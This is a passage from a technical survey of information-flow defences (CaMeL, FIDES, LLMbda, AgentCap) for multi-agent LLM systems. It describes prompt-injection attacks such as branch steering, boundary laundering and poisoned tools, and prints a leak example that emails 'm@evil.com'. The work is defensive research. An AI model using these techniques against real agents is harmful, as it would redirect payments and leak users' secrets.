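| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 64.3% | 20.5% | 26.8% |

Most of the loss came from CaMeL itself. On average, individual CaMeL accounted for 21.6 percentage points and the separate channels for another 3.2. For the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the losses were 13.4 points from individual CaMeL and 0.85 from the separate channels. GPT-4.1 dropped a further 16 points with multi-CaMeL, much more than the average.

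The drop in task completion was often larger on MultiAgentDojo. GPT-4.1 completed 78.4 percent of ordinary tasks without CaMeL, 38.1 percent with individual CaMeL and 24.7 percent with multi-CaMeL. For GPT-5.5, the figures were 86.6, 73.2 and 66.0 percent. On the 45 tasks that Fable 5 didn't refuse, its completion rate was 91.1 percent without CaMeL and 84.4 percent with either version.

The most common cause of failure was a step whose need became clear only after a tool had returned its result. Some AssetOpsBench runs failed less visibly when a sub-agent couldn't find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for something similar. The orchestrator's program, written before the answer arrived, continued without accounting for the substitution.

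All of these tests ran without data policies, so they measure protection against added tool calls but not against a false account number in a call the plan already contains. Stopping that attack would require policies, which would probably further reduce the amount of completed work.

### Steering between planned branches

Untrusted data may decide which branch of a plan runs, even if nobody can add to the plan. Suppose an orchestrator's program asks a payments agent for a refund if a customer's ticket describes a broken product, and otherwise closes the ticket. An attacker can get the refund just by writing that the product is broken. The attack doesn't violate control-flow integrity, since both branches were in the plan, but it violates noninterference because changing an untrusted input changes what the system does.

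Foerster and colleagues named this branch steering and demonstrated it on agents that use a web browser. The planning model routinely included a step to find and dismiss cookie notices. The attacker placed a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement, and the model that reads the screen returned the position of the fake notice's button. The agent clicked it and landed on the attacker's site.

One defence, checking the screen against the page's underlying code, caught simple banners but missed more elaborate ones. Another, asking a second model to confirm what the first had found, failed against an advertisement with pixels altered to mislead the first model.

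Zingrillo and colleagues tried a stricter approach with COBRA. Before the agent sees any untrusted data, the planning model specifies which sites, tools and values each branch may use. In the refund example, it could restrict the refund to the customer's original card and the price paid. COBRA then checks every web request and MCP call against the current branch's limits. It doesn't check clicks, because the same click could open a tab or confirm a bank transfer.

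On the researchers' own benchmark of 101 tasks, attacks succeeded 94.4 percent of the time against an ordinary agent, 89.5 percent against a dual-LLM agent, and never against COBRA. However, the benchmark counts an attack as successful when the harmful action breaks the limits in force at that point, so a system that enforces those limits should score zero.

On the WASP benchmark of attacks on web agents, COBRA blocked all 19 attacks that made forbidden requests, provided the user had approved a description of each site's operations. Without these descriptions, COBRA could only restrict which sites the agent contacted, and all 14 attacks that misused a permitted site succeeded.

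COBRA also fingerprints every tool definition the user approves and halts if a server changes one. It does not detect changes to the code behind a definition. In 13 of the 1,223 cases in MCPTox, a benchmark of poisoned tools, the legitimate and malicious calls were identical and the harm happened out of sight on the server.

### Groups that are not trees

Multi-CaMeL's guarantee covers only trees, where every agent below the top has one parent and agents communicate only through calls and replies. Peters-Gill and colleagues think it could be extended to agents with several parents. A child could treat each new parent as the user of a fresh session. It must not carry its history from one parent to the next, because the history may contain untrusted results that its planning model would then read. Designers would also have to decide what happens when two parents call the same child at once.

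Cycles, direct messages between equals, message queues and shared memory are harder to handle, because a system that uses them may have no top agent whose request fixes the plan and no clear call where an interpreter can separate instructions from data. Peters-Gill and colleagues propose that information should never become more trusted just by passing from one agent to another. They leave a proof for these systems to future work.

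A tree can also gain an agent during a run. If the new agent has one parent and runs under the multi-CaMeL interpreter, the argument for control-flow integrity still holds, because it doesn't depend on the number of agents. But the parent can't use the new agent until the parent's planning model writes a program that calls it.

An agent found through an A2A card is a bigger risk because somebody else runs it. The parent's interpreter can keep tool results out of the message, but it can't control what the other operator's software does with the variables. That software could paste them into its own planning model's context or discard their tags, and either would make boundary laundering possible again.

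When agents share memory, their protection depends largely on how they read it. If an agent reads it through a tool, planted text arrives as a tool result and stays hidden from the planning model. But if a multi-CaMeL agent loaded a file of standing instructions, as OpenClaw does, its planning model would receive whatever another agent had saved there as trusted input, and neither of the interpreter's two rules would apply.

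## FIDES: one label for everything the planner has seen

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a design from Microsoft. Unlike CaMeL, which fixes a program in advance, FIDES lets its planner choose each step after it gets the previous result. To do this safely, FIDES keeps one label for everything the planner has read and checks every tool call against that label.

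### One turn of the loop

The planner is a language model together with the ordinary software that manages its conversation. After each message, it can query the model, call a tool or finish with an answer. The simplest version with label tracking, which Costa and colleagues call the basic planner, works like this:

1. A tool returns a result with a label, such as a web page labeled {U}.
2. The software adds the page to the conversation and raises the context label to the join of the old label and the new one. If the context was { }, it becomes {U}.
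3. The model reads the conversation and proposes a call. The call and every argument the model writes get the context label.
4. The software compares these labels with the tool's policy, and either runs the call or refuses it.
5. The new result gets the join of the labels of the call, its arguments and any stored data the tool read.

For secrecy, FIDES can replace the single mark S with a list of permitted readers. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example in which Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has also emailed Alex. The permitted readers are {Alex, Priya} for Priya's email and {Alex, Marco} for Marco's. Once the agent has read both emails, only people on both lists may read what it writes. Only Alex is on both, so the agent can't send Marco a reply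 without approval. If Priya had copied Marco in, both Alex and Marco would be on both lists, and the agent could send the reply.

Costa and colleagues propose two basic policies. One allows a consequential action only if the call and its arguments are trusted. The other allows data to go only to people who are already allowed to read it, though an injected instruction can still trigger a message to them.

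### Hiding results in variables

FIDES limits label creep by storing some results in variables, as in Willison's dual-LLM pattern, and showing the model only the variable names. It hides a result only if showing it would make the context label more restrictive. In a list of emails, the model might see the dates but only variable names in place of the subjects and bodies.

How much the planner needs to see depends on the task. Suppose the user wants the agent to do something with the three latest emails:

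- **Forward them on Slack.** The planner passes the variable to the messaging tool, and FIDES inserts the text just before the call. The planner chose the call and the recipient in a clean context, so both are labeled { }. Only the message is labeled {U}, and a policy can allow that.
- **Summarise them first.** A quarantined model without tools reads the variable and writes the summary into a new one, also labeled {U}. The planner's context stays clean.
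- **Create a calendar event if one of them asks for a meeting.** The next step now depends on what the emails contain, so the planner has to learn something about them.

In the calendar task, the planner could inspect the emails, but this would raise its context label to {U} and block the calendar tool. Costa and colleagues suggest that the planner instead ask the quarantined model for a yes or no and inspect only the answer. The software forces the answer into the requested form, so it can't contain an instruction.

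To support this, the label also records the value's type. Types are ordered by how much information they can carry, from Booleans through fixed lists of options to free text. A Boolean carries at most one bit, and a choice among eight options at most three, so a policy can accept an untrusted Boolean while refusing untrusted text. Garby and colleagues have criticised this deliberate exception to the integrity rule. An attacker can still choose the value, as in branch steering, by sending an email that asks for a meeting.

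### What the formal model covers

The secrecy property that Costa and colleagues use is called explicit secrecy. Take a run that performs a particular sequence of actions, and let *g* be the combined effect of those actions on the stored data. If two stores *d*₁ and *d*₂ have the same public contents but different secrets, the property requires that

g(d₁) =_L g(d₂),

where =_L means that the public contents are equal. In other words, repeating the same actions with different secrets must not change anything public.

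The paper claims that the loop with label tracking can enforce this property for any planner that runs in it, given a suitable policy. It supports this claim with definitions and a lemma, but not a full proof. It treats the model as deterministic and assumes that attackers control neither the user's messages nor the tool descriptions.

Explicit secrecy is weaker than noninterference because it holds the sequence of actions fixed. Suppose an agent reads a confidential list of redundancies and opens a public web page on employment law only if the user is on the list. If the policy treats opening pages as harmless, anyone who can observe the visit learns something about the list. Explicit secrecy doesn't count this implicit flow as a violation. According to Costa and colleagues, enforcing noninterference would essentially require banning tools with public effects once the agent has called a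 tool that may read secrets.

Taint tracking can also enforce safety properties, which are requirements that something never happen. For example, the software could record past actions and refuse to send mail after the agent has opened a payroll file.

### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues compared FIDES with the basic planner on AgentDojo, averaging over five runs. With GPT-4o and no policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against the basic planner and 21 against FIDES, whose planner could still inspect a variable containing an injection and follow it. With the checks on, none succeeded against either. AgentDojo's scoring counted three successes against FIDES, but the researchers reviewed these by hand and concluded that they were not real successes.

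Plain taint tracking with policy checks was therefore enough to stop the attacks. The advantage of hiding results is that the agent can complete more tasks, as these completion rates, measured without attacks, show. The last column is the simple average of the four settings.

| Model and planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, basic, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 84.3% |
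| GPT-4o, basic, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 41.9% |
| GPT-4o, FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 50.0% |
| o1, basic, no checks | 70.0% | 82.0% | 96.2% | 87.6% | 84.0% |
| o1, basic, with checks | 48.0% | 75.0% | 37.5% | 17.1% | 44.4% |
| o1, FIDES, with checks | 64.5% | 68.0% | 56.2% | 54.3% | 60.8% |

FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than plain taint tracking with GPT-4o and 16 more with o1, a reasoning model that handled the variables better. It did worse in the travel setting, where the policies already allowed many tools to run in an untrusted context. Even with o1, it completed 23 percentage points fewer tasks than the unprotected agent. Some of that loss is intended, because many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy forbids.

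The perfect security score is less impressive given how the researchers labeled the data. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, so the labels covered every place where the benchmark could plant text, whereas a real deployer doesn't have a list of those places.

The other choice was the policy for `send_money`, which checked whether the decision to pay was trusted but ignored the labels of the arguments. An agent could therefore pass the attacker's account number from an invoice to the payment tool without tainting its context. The stricter policy, which also requires trusted arguments, would block this attack but also many ordinary bill payments.

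### Asking the user to release a call

*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) presents a system that pauses when a call breaks the policy and asks the user whether to continue, so a refused call doesn't have to end the task. The paper compares this system with OpenAI's GPTs, which asked users to confirm every tool call. People who see constant requests may start approving them without reading them.

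RTBAS also reduces label creep by hiding parts of the conversation that seem irrelevant to the next step, so that their labels don't count. The version that used a second language model to judge relevance asked for unnecessary confirmation in 8 percent of 37 test cases involving private data, versus 30 percent for a system that always asked. It completed 40 percent of the tasks if the user refused every request and 83 percent if the user approved them all. The study didn't measure how well real users tell a safe request from a dangerous one, and its AgentDojo test simply skipped calls that broke the policy.

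Users can also approve data instead of individual calls. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes PRUDENTIA, a version of FIDES in which the planner can request the user's endorsement of a variable before inspecting it. Suppose an email contains a to-do list with ten items, each of which needs a consequential call. By endorsing the email before the planner inspects it, the user gives one approval instead of ten. But the endorsement covers the whole email, including any planted instruction that the user overlooked.

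PRUDENTIA also gives the planner the labels and policies, so the planner can avoid plans that would need approval. On AgentDojo, PRUDENTIA completed up to 9 percent more tasks than FIDES without human help and cut the number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.9. Kolluri and colleagues counted approvals only in tasks the agent completed, and assumed the user always approved.

### When a tool or agent joins

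FIDES doesn't need a new plan when a tool appears. The planner gives the language model a list of tools with every query, so the software can add a new tool to the next list. The formal model has a fixed set of tools, but it checks each call separately, so the checks can cover a new tool as long as it has a policy for what it accepts and accurate labels for what it returns.

Suppose again that a mail tool is connected after an agent has read a web page and a private file. If FIDES has kept both in variables, the context label is still { }. The user asked the agent to send a summary to a manager, so the planner gives the new tool the manager's address and the summary variable. The decision to send and the address are trusted, and the call passes the checks if the manager may read the private file.

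If the planner had inspected the web page first, its context would still be tainted when the tool became available. The user would have to approve the call, or the agent would have to restart without the page.

In the formal model, every reply from the language model gets the join of the conversation's label and the tool list's label. FIDES gives the tool list the label { } because it assumes the descriptions are trusted. Unless the deployer has vetted a new tool's description, an attack like the one using Invariant Labs' fact server could get past the checks.

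The right label for a tool can also depend on which other tools are present. Zhong and colleagues describe one messaging tool that accepts private data and another that returns sent messages labeled as public. An agent with both tools could send a private message to the user's own account and read it back without the secrecy label. A deployer who adds the second tool therefore has to know what the first one writes. Costa and colleagues' formal model handles this by recording which stored variables each tool reads and writes.

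An agent that joins midway needs the same care, because FIDES normally labels a user's request { }. If FIDES treats another agent's untrusted text as a user's request, it will label that text { } too, which is boundary laundering, as with CaMeL. FIDES could avoid this by putting the untrusted text in a variable, much as multi-CaMeL does.

### Labels in Microsoft's products

In May 2026, Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental feature of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) warned that the software treated a tool as trusted and public if the developer forgot to label it. According to Microsoft's current documentation, the software treats unlabeled tool results as untrusted and public by default.

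The new default is safer for integrity but not for secrecy. Suppose a developer connects a payroll tool during a run and forgets to label its results. The software would treat the salaries as public, so a rule that blocks only private data from public comments would not block them.

Microsoft has also worked with GitHub to add labels to GitHub's MCP server. The server marks files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. GitHub's command-line coding agent, Copilot CLI, can track a context label if the user turns on an experimental setting. Microsoft says the tracking doesn't yet cover all tools or support other MCP servers.

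For other servers, Microsoft has released an open-source gateway that adds the labels. Someone has to define the format of each tool's results, write a function that works out their labels, and write or choose a policy.

A quicker option is to use the hints that MCP servers can attach to their tools. For example, the software could always allow a tool marked as read-only and closed to the outside world. A server can also publish its own policies. But the server's operator writes both the hints and the policies, so this option suits only servers that the deployer already trusts.

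### Labels that last between requests

Memory carries data from one run to the next, so the data's labels have to be kept with it. In the FIDES model, stored variables keep their labels, and a note written in an untrusted context would still be untrusted when the agent read it later. An ordinary file or notebook doesn't record these labels.

After each request, SPA, the system that Girrens and Wang built, saves every result with its label and a short description. When the user makes another request, the planner sees only the descriptions. The planner wrote each description before the tool ran, so the description can't contain anything from the result.

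In the invoice example, Tuesday's planner would see that the agent had saved an invoice on Monday, but not the invoice itself. To use the invoice, the plan must include a step that retrieves it together with its label from Monday. A payment tool that requires trusted input would then refuse the account number. Unlike FIDES, SPA writes a complete plan for each request and checks all of it before running anything.

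To test this, Girrens and Wang split AgentDojo's 97 tasks into sequences of two to five requests. With the label checks on, later plans retrieved the earlier result in 90 percent of the cases where SPA had stored one, and in 73 percent of all cases, including those where it had stored nothing. The checks reduced the share of completed tasks from 62.5 to 35.3 percent.

Attacks succeeded 0.2 percent of the time with the checks and 0.3 percent without them. These results provide little evidence about whether labels protect memory, because the attacks weren't designed to exploit memory. Even when the planner could read the stored values directly, only 0.6 percent of attacks succeeded.

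Saved labels also help when tools change between requests. If the deployer connects a new payment tool on Tuesday and gives it a policy, SPA can check Monday's invoice against that policy. But if an agent copies the invoice to an outside file, the label isn't copied with it, so whoever sets up the tool that reads that file has to label its results as untrusted.

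## LLMbda: a proof that covers agents which write their own code

FIDES checks labels in one fixed loop and guarantees something weaker than noninterference. CaMeL lets a model write a new program for every request, but no theorem covers the interpreter that runs those programs. Garby and colleagues defined a small programming language, LLMbda (pronounced "L-L-Em-da"), and proved noninterference for every program in it, including code that a model writes during the run.

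### A language for conversations

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which programs consist of functions applied to values. Its variables never change once they have a value. The only thing that changes during a run is a conversation with a language model, and four operations act on it:

- `send` adds a prompt to the conversation.
- `recv` (receive) gets the model's reply, adds it to the conversation and runs it as code. The result may be a piece of text, a number or a new function for the program to call.
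- `fork` runs part of the program on a copy of the conversation, then discards the copy and keeps only the result.
- `clear` empties the conversation.

The symbol `@` is shorthand for sending a prompt and receiving the reply.

Every value has a label made of the marks U and S, and so does the conversation as a whole. The model's reply runs with the conversation's label as its control label, so everything the generated code computes gets at least that label. The proof therefore holds whatever the model writes, even if an attacker dictates it.

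Tools are functions in the same language, and each contains its own checks. The instruction `assert` stops the program unless a value's label is within a given limit. For example, a mail function can assert the limit {S} on the subject and body, so the program stops if either has the mark U.

### Isolating an email

The dual-LLM pattern becomes one short function, shown here in simplified notation:

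```
quarantine(prompt) = fork (clear; @prompt)
```

Suppose a user asks an agent to remind Bob about a meeting. Bob's address is in an email labeled {U}, which also contains a planted request to cancel the meeting.

1. The program calls `quarantine` with a request to extract the sender's address, followed by the email. This prompt has the label {U}.
2. `fork` copies the main conversation, whose label is { }, and `clear` empties the copy.
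3. `@` sends the prompt. The copy's label rises to {U}, and so does the label of the reply.
4. `fork` discards the copy. The program now has an address labeled {U}, and the main conversation is still { }.

The same model can answer in both conversations, because the isolation comes from the conversation the model receives. A program that reads only trusted files can omit the function.

Garby and colleagues ran this example with two agents. The first used a single conversation for both the email and its tool calls, followed the planted text and wrote a cancellation. The second wrote its code before reading the email, and sent the reminder. The mail function didn't check the recipient's label, so the theorem doesn't protect the address, and a forged address could still have redirected the reminder.

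`clear` also helps with label creep. It lowers the conversation's label to the current control label, which is safe because the restricted text is gone. Code from an untrusted conversation still has U in its control label, so it can't use `clear` to make itself trusted.

### The assignment that never ran

CaMeL blocks a program that emails an outsider only if an account balance is above some threshold, because the decision to send depends on a secret. But it misses a roundabout version. The example that Garby and colleagues give amounts to this program:

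```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL raises a variable's label only on a branch that actually runs.

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | `tmp` becomes false and secret | Skipped, so `tmp` stays true and public |
| 4 | Skipped, so `rich` stays true and public | `rich` becomes false and stays public |
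| 5 | Sends the email | Sends nothing |

The email goes out exactly when the balance is above the threshold, but the check before sending involves only a public variable. This is the leak Fenton described in the 1970s, with an email as the output.

*Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues, 2015) describes a standard remedy, the no-sensitive-upgrade check. It allows an assignment to *x* only if pc ⊆ label(x), where pc is the control label and label(x) is *x*'s current label. If the balance is high, the check stops the program at line 3, before it can send anything. The check also stops harmless programs, such as one that never uses the variable again. A more lenient version marks the variable as partially leaked and stops the program only if it later tries to use that variable.

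LLMbda needs this check only for the conversation, since its variables never change. Suppose a program tells the model that *x* is false, then, only if a secret is true, tells it to set *x* to true, and finally asks for *x*. If the secret is true, the interpreter blocks the second message because the control label is {S} and the conversation's label is { }. Raising the conversation's label to {S} instead wouldn't be enough, because when the secret is false, the program would skip the message, the conversation would stay public, and the model's answer would reveal the secret.

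Peters-Gill and colleagues accept that multi-CaMeL has the same flaw. They reply that it doesn't affect their argument for control-flow integrity, in which they assume that the interpreter correctly keeps tool output out of the instructions to other agents. This reply applies only to the design. The current software still has the flaw, and they leave fixing it to future work.

Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL treats untrusted values as trusted once a program inserts them into a string. The reply doesn't cover this bug. If multi-CaMeL still has it, an orchestrator could insert a poisoned summary into an instruction without breaking the interpreter's rule.

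### One bit per failed attempt

CaMeL tracks labels inside its interpreter, but an ordinary Python loop outside it tries again when a program fails. Whether a policy blocks the program can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit.

Suppose a balance is a whole number from 0 to 1,023, and a program triggers a policy failure only if the balance is above 511. If the attempt fails, the next one tests 767, and if it succeeds, the next one tests 255. Ten attempts reveal the exact balance. CaMeL censors the error messages it passes to the next attempt, but Garby and colleagues point out that this gives no formal guarantee. Ordinary use is unlikely to cause the leak, because it requires programs written to exploit it.

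Multi-CaMeL doesn't retry, so this leak doesn't affect it. But Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that the usual method of listing hidden channels and narrowing each one may not be enough as agents become more strategic.

### Noninterference when replies are random

Ordinary noninterference compares the outputs of two runs. But a language model samples its replies, so two runs can differ even when their inputs are the same. The definition therefore has to compare the probability of each result. It also has to allow for runs that never finish, either because they loop forever or because a label check stops them.

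Garby and colleagues call their version termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, or TIPNI. Changing data that an observer can't see may change how often the program finishes, but must not otherwise affect the probabilities of what the observer sees.

To make this precise, let the label *m* describe an observer who can see every value whose label is contained in *m*. Take two starting states that look the same to this observer. For each visible result *q*, let μ₀(q) and μ₁(q) be the probabilities that the program finishes with *q* from the first and second state. Each set of probabilities may add up to less than 1, and the shortfall is the chance that the program doesn't finish. TIPNI requires that some function ω exists with

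μ₀(q) ≤ ω(q) and μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

If the unfinished runs had ended in suitable ways, the two sets of probabilities could have been identical. The test is to add up the larger of the two probabilities for each result and check that the total does not exceed 1.

| | Approves | Rejects | Doesn't finish |
|---|---|---|---|
| Secret is A | 60% | 30% | 10% |
| Secret is B | 50% | 40% | 10% |

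The larger figures are 60 and 40 percent, which add up to 100, so TIPNI allows this program. If the program always finished, and approved 60 percent of the time with one secret and 50 percent with the other, the larger figures would be 60 and 50 percent. These add up to 110, so TIPNI would forbid it. Under TIPNI, a program that always finishes must give exactly the same probabilities whatever the secret is.

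The paper also proves a limit on the leak. Half the sum of the differences between the two sets of probabilities is at most the average chance of not finishing. In the table, both values are 10 percent.

If a program always finishes with one secret and never with another, an observer who can tell whether it finished learns one bit. TIPNI permits this leak. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues examine properties that ignore such leaks in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*. The leak can be much larger if the program produces output as it runs. For example, it could print 0, 1, 2 and so on, then hang when it reaches a secret number. LLMbda's theorem compares only the final conversation and result, so it doesn't cover what an outsider could learn from messages sent during the run.

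For integrity, the relevant observer is {S}, who sees everything not marked U. The theorem then means that an attacker's text can't change the probabilities of trusted results, except by affecting whether the program finishes. TIPNI therefore rules out branch steering, as Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge. In the earlier refund example, the branch depends on a customer's ticket, so its control label is {U}, and a refund function that requires trusted arguments would reject the call.

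The proof uses a second way of running each program, which skips any computation whose label the observer can't see and substitutes an empty value. This version gives the same probabilities from both starting states because it ignores the data that differs. It also produces each visible result at least as often as the real program does. Its probabilities can therefore serve as ω.

Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs, has verified the theorem. The interpreter that runs the agents is also written in Lean, and Garby and colleagues proved that it matches the mathematical definition of the language. Flume's proof was not linked to its code in this way. The LLMbda proof does not cover the network request to the model. It assumes that each reply is a random draw that depends only on the current conversation. If a provider let its model remember earlier conversations, `clear` would no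 longer remove everything the model had read.

### Endorsing data without releasing secrets

Some tasks need a trusted value that comes from an untrusted source. For example, an agent might sort an incoming email into one of a few categories and use the category as the subject of its reply. The category is marked U, so the mail function would reject it. LLMbda's `endorse` instruction can remove the mark.

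Endorsement can't remove S. Endorsing a value labeled {U,S} gives {S}, so a secret password stays secret. Weakening integrity therefore doesn't weaken confidentiality. An observer with the label {U} can see all public data, trusted or not. Changing a value's label from {U} to { } shows this observer nothing new because the value was already visible, and changing it from {U,S} to {S} shows nothing because the value stays hidden. The paper proves that TIPNI still holds for this observer, however often a program endorses data and whatever untrusted text an attacker supplies. It calls this result insulated TIPNI. The proof requires the integrity and confidentiality parts of a label to be independent.

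An attacker might try to plant code that contains its own `endorse`. This doesn't work directly, because code made from untrusted text runs with U in its control label, and an endorsed value always keeps the marks in the control label.

The protection fails if an earlier endorsement removed U from the text that became the code. To prevent such chains of endorsements, Garby and colleagues propose a third mark, E, for endorsed data, and a version of `endorse` that refuses any value already marked E. Another version endorses only values from a fixed list. It has to endorse the value before comparing it with the list, because branching on an untrusted value would put U in the control label and make the endorsement useless. The theorems still hold with either version, but the paper doesn't prove how much extra protection they give.

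FIDES's exceptions for implicit flows and small untrusted values are less visible than an explicit `endorse`. Garby and colleagues consider both exceptions defensible, and note that FIDES's tests didn't use the exception for small values. But they object that a reviewer looking at a run can't tell an intended exception from a real leak. Explicit endorsements still have to be checked, and if a model writes a new plan for each request, somebody has to read every plan.

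### An agent that practises first

To test the language, the team built an agent called Randori. A model first writes a plan and tries it on a mock bank account, where payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder text. The model can correct its errors without reading anything untrusted, which avoids CaMeL's retry leak. It then writes a final plan for the real account. This plan can still fail because of a label error, since the mock run doesn't reveal label errors.

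The team tested Randori on AgentDojo's banking tasks, pairing each of 16 user tasks with each of 9 attacks. They ran each of the 144 pairs three times with each of three models, for 1,296 attacked runs. Randori resisted the attack in all but two. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The plan endorsed the file's contents, so the label checks allowed the payment. Without endorsement, Randori blocked this attack but also couldn't do the task.

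In 97 of the 144 combinations, the attack needed a tool call that an ordinary plan for the task wouldn't contain, so writing the plan in advance was normally enough to stop it without the labels. The other 47 combinations are a better test of the labels, and both failures were among them.

These are the shares of user tasks completed without attacks. A dash means that the paper gives no result.

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
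|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0% | 75.0% | 64.6% |
| Randori without endorsement | – | 62.5% | 54.2% |
| CaMeL without policy checks | 66.7% | – | 70.8% |
| CaMeL with policy checks | 37.5% | – | 37.5% |

Randori did about as well as CaMeL did without policy checks, and completed nearly twice as many tasks as CaMeL did with them. With only 16 different tasks, the margins of error are about 20 percentage points either way. The comparison also favours Randori because its policies are looser than CaMeL's. For example, Randori's rule for scheduling a payment requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient.

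With the policy checks on, no attack on CaMeL succeeded in the runs that finished. A few succeeded with the checks off, including two on a task that told the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. CaMeL's planning model had written a loop that could carry out instructions for any available tool, so the attacker only had to put the right instruction in the file and didn't need to change the plan.

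### Several agents and outside tools

LLMbda can represent agents that take turns. One agent can start another with `fork`, give it a request and wait for the result, and the labels stay attached throughout. This prevents the boundary laundering that defeated the three CaMeL agents. If the orchestrator pasted the poisoned summary into its request, the notification agent's conversation would become {U}, and so would any code it wrote. A mail function that required trusted input would then send nothing. To get the summary to Julie, the orchestrator would have to pass it separately from the instruction, as in multi-CaMeL, and the messaging function would have to accept untrusted text.

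The language can't run two agents at once. It has a single current conversation, and a forked part must finish before the rest of the program continues. The theorem therefore doesn't cover agents that exchange messages while both are working, or secrets revealed by which agent finishes first. Extending the theorem to these cases would require rules for shared memory and for the order in which messages arrive.

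The model also assumes that every data source is part of the program, which Garby and colleagues list as a limitation. In the AgentDojo tests, the tools changed a simulated bank account inside the program, and the test software copied the changes out at the end. A real tool can contact the outside world while the program is running. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) describes a loop that contacts a server a secret number of times, so that the server's log reveals the number. It suggests capping such loops or combining the requests into one.

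This model has no equivalent of an MCP server registering a tool or an unknown agent sending a message, so an outside party can't add a link. If a mail tool appears halfway through a task, the deployer can write an LLMbda function for it and start a new program. The theorem holds for every program in the language, so it covers this one without a new proof. It doesn't establish that the function has the right checks or that the tool behaves as the function describes.

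## DelegateGuard and AgentCap: limiting the authority an agent passes on

LLMbda's proof relies on each tool function containing the right checks, including a check that the caller may use the tool. That permission is hard to settle in advance when agents start sub-agents during a run, because a sub-agent needs some of its parent's authority but can't be put on an access list before it exists. AgentCap and DelegateGuard, two designs from late 2026, solve this with capability tokens. The parent passes on part of its authority as a token, and software outside the model checks the token on every call.

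### When having a tool counts as permission

Some popular agent frameworks limit authority mainly by choosing which tools an agent can see. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) audits the public code of LangChain/LangGraph, LlamaIndex and Stripe's toolkit for payment agents. The title's "capability gates" are lists of available tools, not tokens in Hardy's sense. When a model proposes a call, LangChain and LlamaIndex look up the tool by name and run it with the model's arguments, at most checking their format. Stripe's toolkit can restrict the types of action, but it passes on the amounts and customers the model chose. By default, none of the three checks whether the model's specific values are allowed.

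To demonstrate the gap, Mellafe Zuvic gave a LangChain agent a tool that changes the bank account for a merchant's payouts. A script simulated a hijacked model and proposed the account `acct_ATTACKER_999`. LangChain made the change in a mock payment system. ScopeGate, Mellafe Zuvic's own checker, refused the identical call because the operator's list of allowed accounts contained only `acct_MERCHANT_001`. The list has to come from outside the model, or the injection that changes the call could change the list too.

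ScopeGate refused all 48 scripted attacks and all 29 unauthorised calls from a model that could learn from earlier refusals. The scripted attacks had exposed a bug in an earlier version, which accepted a payment whose amount was "not a number" because the comparison with the spending limit didn't fail.

By default, LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen don't narrow the authority that one agent passes to another. Dantuluri and Sundi (2026) found this in *Delegation Without Trust* by running a scripted agent in LangGraph and inspecting the code of the other two. MCP's authorization rules tie a token to one server, but they don't narrow the authority passed between agents either.

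### A chain of tokens in AgentCap

Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, put a policy engine and a gateway between agents and their MCP servers. A token goes through these steps:

1. **Issue.** An agent proposes a call and declares its purpose. The policy engine checks seven conditions, including whether the policy permits that purpose and whether the agent already holds a token that must not be combined with this one. If all seven hold, it signs a token that names the agent, session, action, resource, expiry time and number of calls. In the paper's banking policy, a payment token lasts 30 seconds and covers one call.
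2. **Attenuation.** The holder can derive a token for a sub-agent in the same session, within the limits below.
3. **Signature.** The parent signs the new token, which identifies the token it came from. If the sub-agent edits any field, the signature no longer matches.
4. **Verification.** When the sub-agent makes a call, the gateway starts from its token and works back to the original. At each hop it checks the signature, the limits and whether anyone has revoked the token. Finally, it checks the policy engine's signature on the original token.
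5. **Revocation.** The gateway doesn't rely on earlier results, so revoking one token also disables every token derived from it.

Let *a* be the action, *r* the resource, *b* the number of calls, *e* the expiry time and *d* the number of further hops allowed. The sub-agent's values, marked with a prime, must satisfy

a′ = a, r′ = r, b′ ≤ b, e′ ≤ e, d′ < d.

The sub-agent can therefore do the same thing to the same resource, but no more often and for no longer. Because *d* falls at every hop, the chain must end. The policy's delegation rules apply to types of agent, such as supervisor and worker, so they also cover a worker that starts during the run.

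AgentCap can also revoke tokens automatically. Each agent starts with a trust score of 0.8, and every refused call multiplies it by 0.7. After two refusals the score is 0.39 and the agent loses write access. After three the score is 0.27 and the agent loses all access.

Some designs let a holder narrow a token without contacting the issuer. Veski, Guerraoui and Froelicher (2026), in *CAPMAS*, do this with macaroons, tokens that carry a list of restrictions and a chained signature. For a token limited to reading one folder, the chain could be:

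- sig₀ = HMAC(secret, "request 123")
- sig₁ = HMAC(sig₀, "folder A only")
- sig₂ = HMAC(sig₁, "read only")

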